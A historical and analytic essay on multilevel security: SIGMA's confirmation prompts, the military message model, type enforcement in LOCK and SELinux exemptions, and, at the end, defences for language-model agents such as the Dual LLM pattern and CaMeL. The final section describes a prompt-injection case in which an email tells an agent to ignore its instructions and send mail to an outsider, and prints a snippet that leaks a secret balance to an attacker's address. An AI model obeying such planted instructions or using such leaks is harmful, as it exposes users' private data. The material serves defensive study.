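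The message program, SIGMA, came from the Information Sciences Institute at the University of Southern California. It ran on TENEX, an operating system with no security kernel. According to *Military Message Experiment Final Report* (Wilson, Goodwin and Bersoff, 1982), the designers built the user interface as though there were a kernel, so that the interface could stay the same if one were added later. The experiment therefore provides evidence about users, but little about whether such software could keep secrets.

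SIGMA served each user through up to five processes. One handled unclassified control work, and each of the three classified levels had its own process. These four could write only at their own level and read only at that level or below. The fifth, a trusted process, could move information to a lower level.

The earliest design had no trusted process and failed because of the reply command. Suppose an officer reads a Secret message and wants to send a Confidential answer. The command fills in the addressees, subject and references from the original, which copies text from a Secret object into a Confidential one. Under a strict star-property, the officer would have to retype those fields. Users found this unacceptable in early discussions, so the designers added the trusted process.

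*SIGMA Final Report* (Stotz, Wilczynski and colleagues, 1982) describes how the system's trusted process handled user commands. When a user pressed a function key, the trusted process interpreted the key directly and accepted it. A typed command first passed through SIGMA's untrusted code, where a Trojan horse could have altered the command or invented one. So if the command affected security, the trusted process asked the user to confirm it by pressing a YES key. Pressing NO or CANCEL stopped the operation.

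The trusted process also controlled two sets of lights on the terminal. One showed the level of the window the user was typing in, and the other showed the highest level anywhere on the screen. A classification printed in the message came from untrusted code, so users were supposed to compare it with the lights.

Users had some other security duties:

- They had to choose a level for each message before writing it. The designers had considered starting every draft at Top Secret and letting the author lower it at the end, but then the author would have had to review the whole text for downgrading. On paper the problem hardly arises, because, as Landwehr points out, an author can lock an unmarked draft in a safe and classify it later.
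- They had to read any text that they were taking out of a message to downgrade, and verify that it contained nothing too sensitive for its new level.
- Somebody had to release each outgoing message. SIGMA then returned a copy to the releaser, which Wilson and colleagues count as a final security check, although by then the message had already gone.

### What users made of the prompts

Interviews at the end of the experiment showed that few users understood the security model or knew what the lights and confirmation keys were for. Many thought the keys were an unnecessary bother. Stotz and colleagues report that users found the prompts "somewhat annoying and stupid", though not a major aggravation. The users "never understood" that the prompts were there to check SIGMA.

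Wilson and colleagues give three reasons. The system was late, so the users with the most security training had moved to other posts before it was ready, and their replacements heard less about security. Everyone worked in an area controlled for Top Secret material and rarely had to think about who was cleared for what. And users completely trusted computers to protect classified information, although security tests on other systems had shown this trust to be wrong in almost every case.

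The form of the question probably mattered too. When a user types a command to reply at Confidential, the terminal displays a prompt asking whether the user really wants to do that. As long as the software is not malicious, the answer is always yes, except after a typing mistake. The prompt is useful mainly when a hostile program attempts something the user did not request, and by then the user may have pressed YES hundreds of times without a reason to press anything else.

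The interviews showed that SIGMA's users did not know what they were confirming, and most of them probably approved transfers without thinking. How often they would have caught a bad transfer is unknown, because the evaluation of SIGMA's security features gives no count of prompts, approvals or refusals and describes no trial in which somebody planted a false request to see who would notice. SIGMA also never received a Top Secret message, so users never had to answer a prompt about the most sensitive kind of material.

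Users accepted reviewing text before a downgrade more readily than the confirmation prompt, and only a few objected to it. Review took more work than pressing a key, but it resembled what officers already did with paper. It also had them judge the contents of a message, which they were qualified to do, rather than whether a program could be trusted.

Both final reports conclude that users would accept a future system with this kind of interface. That seems right, since users tolerated the controls and the headquarters removed SIGMA mainly because it was unreliable and could not serve enough of the staff. However, the controls may fail to protect anything even if users accept them.

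A better argument for the prompts, from Wilson and colleagues, is that they help even when users don't understand them. A hostile program in the trusted part of the system can downgrade something only when a user presses the key, which limits how often it can leak information but not how much it can leak each time. If a user confirms 30 transfers a day without reading what is being transferred, the program has 30 chances a day to leak a whole document.

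### A model of the message system itself

Researchers at the Naval Research Laboratory concluded that the security model should describe the message system people use. *A Security Model for Military Message Systems* (Landwehr, Heitmeyer and McLean, 1984) sets out such a model for a family of systems, with an informal version that users can read and a formal one for designers.

The laboratory first objected that Bell–LaPadula gives each object a single level. The paragraphs of a military document may have different classifications, and so may the messages in a file. If the file as a whole is Secret, taking a Confidential message out of it counts as a write-down, even though no secret information has moved. Bell–LaPadula also cannot express rules that belong to the application, such as who may release a message. Designers therefore have to put ordinary operations into trusted processes, and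 the rules that the system actually enforces end up in the code of those processes, where users cannot find them. The laboratory argued that people who understand the rules make fewer accidental disclosures. The SIGMA interviews support at least the concern about understanding, since officers working under a simulated kernel did not understand the rules.

In the new model, everything that holds information is an *entity*. An entity is either an *object*, which has one classification and no classified parts, or a *container*, which has its own classification and may hold objects and other containers. Some containers are marked "Container Clearance Required" (CCR), and a user needs clearance for the whole of such a container to see anything inside it. Each user has a clearance and a set of *roles*, such as releaser, downgrader or system security officer, which permit particular operations.

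The model makes ten assertions about what the system must enforce. The ones that matter most for downward flow are these:

- A container's classification is at least as high as that of anything in it.
- Information taken out of an object keeps the object's classification, and the system may not insert it into an object with a lower one.
- Whenever the system displays an entity, it displays the classification too.
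- Nobody can lower a classification except a user who holds the downgrader role and has given a command to downgrade.
- Nobody can release a draft message except a user who holds the releaser role, and the system records that user's identity in the message.

Four assumptions cover what the system cannot enforce. The first is that the security officer assigns clearances, roles and device levels correctly. The other three are that users give the right classification whenever they write, edit or reclassify something, address messages only to people who need to know the contents, and take care with anything they remove from a CCR container.

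The second assertion resembles the star-property, but it governs which information moves, while Bell and LaPadula's rule governs which files a program has open. It can therefore tell apart the two versions of the program that read the convoy report. If the weather paragraph is marked Unclassified and the route Secret, the version that copies the weather obeys the assertion and the version that leaks the route breaks it. The model has no trusted subjects because its subjects are people. It trusts them to write at the right level, as the paper system did, a point made in *Multilevel Object Security Model* (Sullivan, Lunt and Proctor, 1986).

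The assertion about downgrading also applies to McLean's System Z, which lowers every label at once. The assertion governs changes of label as well as the resulting state, so System Z violates it unless a downgrader has requested the change. Bell's artillery observers could still use their self-erasing computer if someone held the downgrader role.

### One message from draft to release

*Specifications for Three Members of the Military Message System (MMS) Family* (Heitmeyer and Cornwell, 1985) lists the commands that such systems would offer. The simplest system only displays and files incoming messages, the second can also compose and send messages, and the third, M2, adds formal messages and commands for the security officer.

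Suppose a lieutenant with a Secret clearance wants to send a harbour an Unclassified message containing the weather forecast and arrival date from the convoy report. The report is a Secret container with the CCR mark. Its weather paragraph is Unclassified, and the paragraph that gives the route and arrival date is Secret.

| Step | Who acts | What the model requires |
|---|---|---|
| Create a draft marked Unclassified | Lieutenant | The lieutenant has chosen the right level (an assumption) |
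| Display the report | Lieutenant | The lieutenant's clearance and the terminal's level are at least Secret |
| Copy the weather paragraph into the draft | Lieutenant | The paragraph's level is no higher than the draft's, so the copy succeeds |
| Copy the arrival date into the draft | Lieutenant | The date keeps its Secret classification, so the system refuses |
| Lower the classification of an extract containing only the date | Downgrader | The user holds the role and gives an explicit command |
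| Add the extract and circulate the draft for comment | Lieutenant and colleagues | The extract is now Unclassified, so the copy succeeds |
| Read the draft and send it | Releaser | The user holds the role, and the system records who it was |

Copying the weather information requires neither an exemption nor a prompt. SIGMA protected every part of a received message at the level of the whole message, so copying it there would have been a downgrade. The new system requires special authority in only two cases, and in both a person must judge what a text reveals. In M2, users can edit a draft but cannot change its classification, so anyone who starts at the wrong level must begin a new message.

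The lieutenant could also have read the arrival date on the screen and typed it into the Unclassified draft. None of the model's assertions forbids this, because the system cannot tell where typed words come from. The model relies on the assumption the military has always made, that cleared people behave properly. The releaser might notice the date. But a user can hold several roles at once, so the lieutenant could be the author, downgrader and releaser unless the security officer assigns those roles to different people.

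### What a separate model costs

One objection to application-specific models is that somebody has to write a new one for each application and then prove that a system satisfies it. Bell–LaPadula was ready to use, and it describes a mechanism primitive enough to verify. Sullivan and colleagues point out that with the laboratory's model, all the software up to the user interface needs verification. For example, somebody has to examine the message program to show that it never copies Secret text into an Unclassified draft.

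By describing the system as users see it, the laboratory removed the exemption from the model. But the code that would have needed the exemption is still there, and the trusted computing base now also includes the rest of the message program. Wilson and colleagues estimated that programs like SIGMA had around half a million instructions and thought it impossible to verify one.

Sullivan and colleagues also object that nobody had formally proved that the model satisfied its own axioms. The Defense Department required such a proof for an A1 rating, and it would have been the model's version of the Basic Security Theorem. McLean, who had helped to write the message model, thought little of such theorems, so the gap may not have troubled him, though it would have troubled a contractor who needed the rating.

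The paper's own proposal, written at the company Sytek for the Air Force, is a compromise. A trusted "object handler" stores containers and their parts and enforces the rule that a container's level dominates its contents. The programs that present messages to users run on top of it and are untrusted. The paper supplies the missing proof for this smaller model. The design reduces the amount of trusted software, but the untrusted part now includes software between the stored message and the person who has to approve its release.

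Payne, Moore and Mihelcic (1994) acknowledge in *An Experience Modeling Critical Requirements* that nobody ever built a trustworthy version of the laboratory's message system. They worked at the same laboratory and tried the approach on something smaller, an encryption device with a bypass for headers, much like the one in Rushby's example. To avoid starting afresh for each device, they wrote one model for the whole class, with eight assertions and eight parameters that a designer fills in. One assertion requires the length of every message to belong to a permitted set. If the set has only one member, all messages are the same length and nobody can signal by varying it, but a set containing every whole number allows any length.

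The network's performance requirements ruled out the strict settings for message length, bypass length and transmission rate in the device they built. They also knew too little about the traffic to restrict the context of messages. Four of the eight assertions therefore had no effect, and the network compensated by encrypting everything a second time. They did verify that the implementation satisfied the remaining assertions. This is decent evidence that a model can serve a family of applications and that a small system can be verified against it, but it isn't evidence about releasers and downgraders, because the device has no human users.

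When a conference reprinted the 1984 paper in 2001, Landwehr and colleagues described it as the first paper in an archival journal to base a security model on the needs of an application instead of the structure of an operating system. They also credited it with introducing access controls based on user roles. They thought their way of developing the informal model remained "quite relevant", and that many later efforts to argue systematically for a system's security could be related to it. These claims about their method are fair. SELinux, for instance, includes roles in its controls.

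### What a person at a screen can check

Letting a user decide what to release has advantages. The user has a clearance, faces legal penalties for abusing it, and may know that an innocent-looking date would reveal an operation. A filter could catch that date only if somebody had thought to program it to. The system can also record who released what, so that an investigator knows whom to question.

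The user approves an image on a screen, but the system sends a file. Landwehr observes that even recording a document's classification may involve a terminal handler, an editor, a file system and a disk handler, written by different people in different languages. A fault in any of them could make the label or text on the screen differ from what is on the disk. If a program shows the releaser a weather report but sends a route, the route is disclosed even though the releaser followed every rule, and the system will record the releaser as the person responsible.

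SIGMA's designers saw this and put the lights under the control of the trusted process. Because the lights did not depend on the code that displayed the message, they could expose a false label, but they could not expose false text. To protect against false text, the trusted software has to draw the text itself, as the Guard's kernel was supposed to do for the watch officer. Wilson and colleagues expected the problem to spread as terminals acquired more programmable code, and thought a terminal might eventually need its own security kernel.

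With a reliable display, the user would only have to judge the content, which people can sometimes do well. It would also help to ask less often. In the worked example, paragraph labels removed one of the two downgrades that SIGMA would have required, and each downgrade removed gives users one less occasion to press YES out of habit. The same applies to language-model agents that ask their users to approve actions. It would also help if the prompt went to someone other than the person in a hurry to send the message. SIGMA asked whoever had typed the command to confirm it, and that person nearly always wanted the operation to go through. The laboratory's model allows somebody else to be appointed, but leaves that choice to the security officer.

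## Type enforcement in LOCK and SELinux

No matter who decides that a message may be sent to a lower level, a program has to move it, and a program exempt from the star-property can usually move much more than that message. Boebert and Kain (1985) proposed a way to limit what such a program can reach in *A Practical Alternative to Hierarchical Integrity Policies*. They were designing the Secure Ada Target (SAT), a machine that Honeywell hoped would exceed the A1 grade, and the project aimed to use trusted subjects as little as possible.

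One objection to trusted subjects is that trust is granted to a subject, but the code that might misbehave is in the program the subject runs. A verifier therefore has to prove that no hostile program can ever run in the trusted subject, which means examining the complicated low-level software that starts programs. The verifier must also work out what the policy was for, turn that into a precise property, and prove the property for every program the subject could run.

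### A labeller that other programs can bypass

Boebert and Kain's main example is a printer that must mark every page with its classification. A verified program, the labeller, looks up a file's level and inserts the marking at the top and bottom of each page. An output program then sends the result to the printer. The raw text and the marked text have the same level, so a hostile program can pass unmarked text straight to the output program, or strip the markings on the way, without violating the star-property or any other secrecy rule.

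Designers had tried to close such gaps with integrity levels, whose rules invert the star-property. In the strictest version, a program may not alter anything of higher integrity or read anything of lower integrity. If raw and marked text have the same integrity level, the rules apply equally to both, and a hostile program can alter the marked text before it reaches the printer. The same is true if the marked text has a lower level. A higher level would be natural, since a verified program produced the marked text, but the labeller would then be turning low-integrity input into high-integrity output, which the rules forbid. Boebert and Kain concluded that every module in the chain would need an exemption.

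### Domains, types and two tables

Their alternative, type enforcement, drops the idea that everything has a place on a scale. Each subject runs in a *domain* and each object has a *type*, and both are simply names. One table lists, for every domain and type, whether programs in that domain may observe or modify objects of that type. Another lists which domains may call programs in which others. For the labeller, the two tables together are:

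| Domain | Unlabelled text | Labelled text | May call |
|---|---|---|---|
| User | observe, modify | nothing | Labeller |
| Labeller | observe | observe, modify | Output |
| Output | nothing | observe | nothing |

Suppose a hostile program in the user domain tries to print a Top Secret memo without its markings. It cannot call the output program, and it cannot add the memo to the labelled text, because it has no access to that type. It can only call the labeller. SAT then suspends the hostile program and starts a new subject in the labeller domain, with that domain's rights. The labeller reads the memo, writes a marked copy and calls the output program, which can read the copy but not change it. The example omits a column for the printer, which is needed so that only the output domain can write to it.

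Boebert and Kain call this arrangement an assured pipeline. Their argument that it is secure has five parts:

1. The hardware enforces the tables.
2. Only the labeller can write labelled text.
3. The output program can read nothing but labelled text.
4. The labeller puts the right marking in the right places.
5. The output program does not tamper with the markings.

The hardware claim is part of the proof of the whole machine. Anyone can confirm claims 2 and 3 by reading the table. Claim 4 needs a modest program proof showing that the labeller looks up the marking correctly and can find the top and bottom of a page. Claim 5 relies on inspection and testing, because output programs are too complex and device-dependent for formal proof. The testing is easier than usual because all the input comes from verified code.

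Earlier proofs about labellers had generally covered only claim 4, and occasionally claim 5. They showed that the labeller worked correctly when called, but not whether text could bypass it and still reach the printer. Boebert and Kain compared this to declaring a system correct because each module had passed its own tests, before anyone had tested them together.

### Applying the tables to a downgrader

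The same method can confine the program that releases replies in a guard. The designer gives approved replies one type and outgoing messages another, then lets the release program read only approved replies and modify only outgoing messages. If the program is hostile, it can leak what is in the approved replies, but it can't read anything else, such as war plans.

Under Bell and LaPadula's access matrix, an exempt program also needed an entry for every file, but the matrix is discretionary, so the holder of a file can add entries to it. In the SAT prototype, the tables were fixed once the reference monitor was installed. SAT could also assign types to program files and restrict which domains could execute them. This ties the power to particular code, which answers the complaint that trust belongs to subjects.

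Types can also enforce an order of events, which the Bell–LaPadula model could not express for the ACCAT Guard. If only the program that displays a reply to the watch officer can create objects of the type "approved reply", and the release program can read only that type, then every reply must pass through the display program before release, though someone still has to verify the display program.

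The tables could not authorize a write-down, however. SAT checked security levels, then the file's list of permitted users, then the type table, and each check could only remove rights. If a Secret process asks to modify an Unclassified buffer, the check on levels removes the right, and no entry in the type table can restore it. Boebert and Kain mention that certain domains had privileged roles and could get more access than the checks on levels and users allowed, but their paper does not describe the mechanism. A downgrader on SAT therefore still needed an exemption. Type enforcement limited that exemption to a short list of things, much as an intransitive policy lets High reach Low only through a named domain.

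### Limiting an exemption by level

GEMSOS instead limited exemptions by level, with a ceiling on what a program could read and a floor on what it could write. Williams calls such a program partially trusted to the extent that its floor does not dominate its ceiling. In a guard between a Secret and an Unclassified network, the release program needs a ceiling of Secret and a floor of Unclassified, so the range allows it to copy any Secret file into any Unclassified one. The type table would limit it to approved replies and outgoing messages. If the same machine also held Top Secret replies of the approved type, the range would keep the program from reading them but the table would not, so a careful designer could use both controls.

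Levels can imitate types. Williams suggests keeping the data the system uses to identify users at a level incomparable with any user's level, so that only certain administrative programs can reach it. Those programs may then need partial trust to read anything else. The designers of an integrity scheme for GEMSOS went further in a paper that appeared beside Boebert and Kain's in a 1989 workshop report. They argued that isolated compartments, with certified programs to move data between them, matched the assured pipeline precisely.

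Compartments and type enforcement seem to give equivalent protection, though with compartments the pipeline has to be built out of trusted subjects. The labeller is then an exception to the general rule, and the verifier needs a separate argument about how far the exception extends. In the type table, the labeller's access is an ordinary entry, and the verifier can read down a column to check that nothing else can write labelled text.

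### What the LOCK proofs covered

Honeywell's team carried type enforcement into LOCK, the Logical Coprocessing Kernel, under a government contract awarded in 1987. Honeywell spun the team off two years later as Secure Computing Corporation. Smith (2001), in *Cost Profile of a Highly Assured, Secure Operating System*, puts the cost of the work up to 1992 at about $23 million.

LOCK made its access decisions on a separate processor, which held the authoritative copy of the tables. The main processor consulted it whenever a program tried to open a file. The trusted computing base had 115,887 lines of code, almost all in C, and fewer than 1,000 of them ran in the processor's most privileged mode. About a quarter of the code was in "kernel extensions", trusted programs that the designers added without enlarging the basic kernel. Type enforcement gave these programs the access they needed to security-critical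 data.

The LOCK mathematicians wrote a formal policy, based on noninterference, and a formal description of everything the TCB offered to other programs. They proved that the described design satisfied the policy, but they proved nothing about the C code. The team systematically matched the description to the code for LOCK's data structures and two services. For one service, the team also compared test results with a simulation driven by the description. The proof checker was so slow that one mathematician kept three Lisp machines busy, and some people questioned the checker's soundness. The team had more success with proofs written for other mathematicians to read.

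This formal work added 58% to the cost of developing the trusted software and found 68% of the flaws that the project detected in LOCK's multilevel security. Secure Computing never completed an A1 evaluation. The company was new and struggling, and the evaluators might have demanded expensive revisions.

By 1992 few customers wanted a time-sharing computer of this kind, so the company turned LOCK into the Standard Mail Guard, which carried e-mail between Secret and unclassified networks from 1994. Users on the Secret side had to review each message before sending it to the unclassified side. The guard's application software bypassed LOCK's multilevel security, and Smith admits that this "rendered the formal analysis irrelevant". The proof now showed that the machine enforced levels correctly except when privileged software bypassed them, as the guard was meant to do. The policy left the application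 to be checked by some other, unspecified process. In later releases the company extended the policy to specify how the guard should behave, which made the proof relevant again.

In the meantime, the guard depended heavily on testing. One test ran subjects in every domain against every other domain and type to confirm that the machine enforced the table. In a 90-day study, the team found about 205 flaws, only 24 of which concerned multilevel security. According to Cryptosmith's *LOCK*, the company eventually deployed a couple of dozen systems in military command centres.

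LOCK's formal policy centred on security levels, as the evaluation criteria required, but the guard's security depended on its filters and on the table that forced messages through them. Although the table could confine the exempt software, the original theorem specified little about what that software should do.

### Which programs the table shows to be trusted

The benefit of the table to designers is clearer in a later system, LOCK6. Hoffman's *Implementing RBAC on a Type Enforced System* describes a guard with two mail programs, each connected to one network, and a chain of filters for each direction. The outward filters may read internal messages and write external ones. The internal mail program may read and write only internal messages. The mail programs are large bodies of borrowed code that nobody wants to verify, and because of the table, they don't have to be trusted with the filtering.

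The administrator of this guard runs diagnostic programs on the mail software and also edits the filter settings. If access depended only on the administrator's identity, a Trojan horse in a diagnostic program could rewrite the filters. In LOCK6, the diagnostics run in a domain that cannot modify files of the filter-configuration type. Hoffman, Greve and Smith's *Using Type Enforcement to Assure a Configurable Pipeline* extends the approach to guards whose administrators choose the filters and their order, using type enforcement to link the chosen filters into a pipeline.

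The table also helps find programs that are trusted in practice but were never declared so. LOCK6 keeps the list of users and their roles in files of one type, and Hoffman observes that a search of the table finds every domain that can modify those files. Every program in those domains has to be checked. In KSOS, a similar search would have found the clearance-file editor, which Ford Aerospace had classed as untrusted.

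### The write rule in SELinux

Type enforcement reached a much wider audience when the NSA released its security additions to Linux, now known as SELinux. The release incorporated Boebert and Kain's idea, according to Linux Journal's *Some Thoughts on the Occasion of the NSA Linux Release*. Every SELinux system checks types. If the administrator installs a multilevel policy, SELinux also checks security levels, and an access must pass both checks.

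Under the multilevel policy, every process and file has a type and a range of levels. For a process, the low end of the range is its current level and the high end is its clearance. In the policy language, t1, l1 and h1 are the type, low end and high end of the process, and t2, l2 and h2 are those of the file. The operators "dom", "domby" and "eq" mean "dominates", "is dominated by" and "equals".

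The rule for writing, as it appears in a copy of the policy from the Linux distribution CentOS, also covers appending to, creating, deleting and renaming files. It permits the operation if any one of five clauses is true:

| Clause | What it permits |
|---|---|
| `l1 eq l2` | Any process may write to a file at its own working level. |
| `t1 == mlsfilewritetoclr and h1 dom l2 and l1 domby l2` | A process of a listed type may write upward, as far as its clearance. |
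| `t2 == mlsfilewriteinrange and l1 dom l2 and h1 domby h2` | Any process may write to a file of a listed type if the file's range contains the process's range. |
| `t1 == mlsfilewrite` | A process of a listed type may write to a file at any level. |
| `t2 == mlstrustedobject` | Any process may write to a file of a listed type, whatever their levels. |

In SELinux, a process working at Secret with a Top Secret clearance can write only to Secret files unless it has an exemption. This is stricter than the star-property, which would also let it append to Top Secret files. The `mlsfilewritetoclr` clause allows this, so it exempts the process from SELinux's rule but not from the star-property. A process covered by the `mlsfilewrite` clause is a trusted subject in Bell and LaPadula's sense, because it can also write to Unclassified files.

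The two remaining exemptions belong to files, whereas Bell and LaPadula exempted only subjects. A file whose range runs from Unclassified to Top Secret can accept data from the Secret process under `mlsfilewriteinrange`, and a process working at Unclassified can then read it. For a trusted object, SELinux doesn't compare levels at all. This is harmless for a device that discards whatever programs send it. But if the type rules let a Top Secret program write to a trusted object and an Unclassified program read it, secrets can move down even though neither program is exempt, and a list of exempt subjects would not show this path.

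The in-range clause was added in 2006 after a mailing-list discussion. A participant suggested that "we could add another 'or'" to the constraint, and Anderson (2006) replied with a tested patch in *New MLS constraint?*. Fedora's changelog describes the result as a constraint exemption for files.

### Who holds the exemptions

A policy writer exempts a type by adding it to one of these lists, which SELinux calls attributes, usually with a one-line call in a policy module. CentOS's *Multilevel security policy* describes the call for `mlsfilewrite` as making a domain "MLS trusted" for writing to files at all levels. The call was originally named `mls_file_write_down`, and its newer name, `mls_file_write_all_levels`, describes more accurately how much it allows. Separate calls cover reading at all levels and raising or lowering a file's label. AlmaLinux's copy of the policy handles lowering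 through an attribute named `mlsfiledowngrade`.

Most distributions build their policies from a shared source, the reference policy. The newest version listed in SELinux Project's *Releases* is 2.20260312, dated 12 March 2026, which added five modules. The number of exempt domains can vary between systems because each distribution chooses which modules to build, administrators can add their own, and any module can grant an exemption with one line. An auditor therefore has to count the exempt domains in the compiled policy on a particular machine, where standard tools can print the members of each attribute. The auditor should also count the exempt file types.

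The domain `systemd_tmpfiles_t` is an example of how a program joins the list. It covers the Linux service that creates temporary files and deletes old ones, much like the spooler's cleanup. Fan and Zhao, engineers at the software company Wind River, wrote a patch for embedded systems that gives the domain four exemptions: reading at all levels, writing at all levels, raising labels and lowering them. They marked the patch as unsuitable for the shared policy. With these exemptions, the check on levels prevents little, and any real confinement comes from the type rules.

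Another example is `staff_t`, the domain of ordinary staff users. *Allowing MLS users to edit files on lower levels*, from Red Hat's documentation for its commercial Linux, explains how to exempt such a domain with a small local module. Red Hat warns that writing to a lower-level file will raise the file to the user's working level, which would keep the new text from leaking. But the write rule doesn't change labels, so this protection probably depends on how the editor saves the file. A Trojan horse running in `staff_t` could append to the existing file directly. Exempting a user's domain exempts every program that runs in it, which is what Boebert and Kain wanted to avoid.

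The multilevel policy has no blanket exemption. It leaves out the module for "unconfined" users, so even root, the Linux superuser, cannot reach every object, as Red Hat's *Using Multi-Level Security (MLS)* explains. Linux Mint's package description, *selinux-policy-mls*, says that developers created the policy for a security certification of Red Hat's system, and recommends it only for students of military security features. The policy has few users, so errors in its lists of exemptions may well last longer than errors in the ordinary policy.

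### How far a narrow exemption can go

For guards, *Security Anti-Pattern* argues that type enforcement should replace the star-property completely. A process that receives messages can be allowed to write to a virus scanner but not to read from it, and the scanner can be allowed to write to the outgoing process. The blog post adds the case of a guard between two coalition partners, where neither side is higher than the other, so a rule against writing down is meaningless. Smith's experience with the mail guard supports the argument, because proving that a machine enforces a policy achieves little if all the important software on it is exempt from that policy.

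Type enforcement works well for guards because each program in the pipeline has one source and one destination. *Multilevel Security* describes a harder case, a trusted word processor that an intelligence analyst uses to reduce a Top Secret document to a Secret one. The program has to open whatever the analyst is working on and save the result where other people can read it. The type table can stop it from changing the audit log or the clearance file, but can't deny it the documents it could leak, because it needs them for its work. Its code is also far larger than a labeller's. The database server that answers users at every level has the same problem.

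Even a short list of exempt types takes work to interpret, because membership in `mlsfilewrite` shows only that levels don't restrict a domain's writing. To learn what the domain can actually write, an auditor also has to read its type rules, follow the files it writes to the programs that read them, and look for trusted objects along the way. Software can do much of this tedious work. The reference policy's developers added automated checks in 2024 and removed some "concerning permissions" that the checks uncovered.

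For programs with narrow jobs, type enforcement supplies some of the guidance Landwehr had found missing. It limits the damage a mistake can do and shows verifiers which programs to check. It cannot distinguish a correct downgrade from a leak when both use the same types, so verifiers must still prove separately that the labeller marks pages properly, or that a filter removes the right sentences.

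SELinux does make the membership of S′ public. Bell's model allowed any set of subjects, but an SELinux policy file lists each exempt type, and the file's history may record who added the type and why. Fan and Zhao's patch, for instance, includes a log entry showing that the kernel had refused `systemd_tmpfiles_t` access to a directory. The entry is evidence that the program couldn't do its job under the existing policy. It doesn't demonstrate that the program would not leak information, which Bell had asked for with exempt programs.

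## A language model as the trusted planner

Designers of language-model agents face a choice much like Bell's choice of S′. An agent that can read a user's files and send mail needs a rule about what it may send to whom, and the designer must decide whether the model may override that rule. Several recent designs allow this only if the model has read nothing an attacker could have written. Boebert and Kain relied on a similar condition when they accepted testing instead of proof for their output program, because all its input came from verified code.

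### Tools and planted instructions

A language model only produces text, so an agent also needs ordinary software to act on that text. The software gives the model the user's request and a list of tools, which are functions for tasks such as searching a mailbox, sending a message or paying a bill. When the model writes a request for a tool, the software runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and calls the model again. This continues until the model writes a final answer. The agent's planner is the model that decides which tools to call, in what order and with what arguments.

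The user's instructions and the tools' results reach the planner as one stream of text, and nobody knows a reliable way to make a model obey one part and only read the rest. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to summarize recent emails about a project and send the summary to the user's manager. One of the emails contains a prompt injection, which tells the agent to ignore its instructions and send the top message in the mailbox to an outside address. If the planner complies, it acts with the user's access, as a Trojan horse does, but the attacker only had to send an email rather than get a program installed.

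Developers have tried filtering out such text and training models to resist it. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) cites a 2025 study whose attacks defeated a combination of two such defences every time and twelve others with similar ease. Many agents also ask the user to approve each risky action. According to *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026), the AI company Anthropic found that users of its coding agent approve about 93% of these requests and pay less attention as the requests accumulate. SIGMA's users similarly pressed the YES key without knowing what it was for.

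### Two models and a controller

The programmer Simon Willison proposed a different approach, which keeps hostile text away from the planner. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, divides the work between two language models. A privileged model plans and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools, and the designer assumes that it may start working for an attacker at any moment. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes data between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the agent works as follows:

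1. The controller gives the request to the privileged model, which asks for the latest email.
2. The controller fetches the email, stores it as $VAR1 and tells the privileged model only that name.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of $VAR1. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as $VAR2.
4. The privileged model asks to display $VAR2, and the controller shows its contents to the user.

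The privileged model can therefore direct the movement of data it cannot read. Willison allows one exception, when the quarantined model only has to sort a text into one of a few fixed categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of those categories and pass it on.

The protection assumes that the user's request is safe. A user who pastes web page text into the request gives the attacker direct access to the planner. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists trust in the initial prompt as a gap in a later version of the design. Willison called the whole proposal "pretty bad", mainly because it makes an assistant more complicated and less pleasant to use, and because a single mistake in the controller could leak untrusted text to the planner.

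### CaMeL and the origin of each argument

In *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind described another gap and a system called CaMeL to close it. Suppose the user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and the meeting notes contain both the document's name and Bob's address. The planner never sees the notes, but the quarantined model has to read them. If an attacker has edited the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address, and the planner's sensible plan will send the document there.

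Willison (2025) explains the remedy in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. CaMeL's planner writes its whole plan in advance as a program in a restricted form of Python. To send Bob a reminder, for instance, the program fetches the last email, has the quarantined model extract Bob's address from it, and calls the mail tool with that address. A special interpreter runs the program and attaches tags, called capabilities, to every value to record where it came from and who may read it. Bob's address inherits the tags of the email that contained it, so the interpreter can detect that an outsider may have chosen the address.

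Before each tool call, the interpreter consults a policy. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), a policy is a Python function that inspects the call and its arguments, then returns a decision to allow or deny the call, with a reason. A policy for the mail tool might allow addresses the user already trusts and ask the user about the rest. The planner cannot falsify the tags because the interpreter sets them, as *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) points out. But because each policy checks one call at a time, CaMeL has no natural way to state a rule about a whole run.

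Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates an office suite, a travel agency, a bank and the workplace chat program Slack, and plants injections in the data that the agent reads. They wrote that CaMeL "effectively solves" the benchmark. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all of the attacks with comparable performance on the users' tasks. Performance can drop much more when the tasks themselves depend on untrusted data. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that switching on CaMeL's policy checks halves the share of banking tasks it completes.

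Garby and colleagues also found ways for secrets to get past the tags. Take this program, in which the bank balance is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(attacker, "rich")
```

If the balance exceeds the threshold, the third line sets `tmp` to false and tags it as secret. The fourth line then doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and public, and the last line sends the email. If the balance is lower, `tmp` stays true, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out, so the attacker learns whether the balance exceeds the threshold. CaMeL can tag a variable according to the conditions it depends on, but only for assignments that run. A second leak comes from the ordinary Python code outside the interpreter that retries a plan after a failure. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on one bit of a secret, so with enough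 retries a program can reveal the whole secret one bit at a time.

In CaMeL, such a program has to come from the planner, so an attacker who cannot reach the planner would find it hard to plant one. The leaks therefore matter most to a designer who wants the checks to constrain the planner too. CaMeL has no proof that its checks do this, and its designers called a formal treatment a "crucial direction" for later work.

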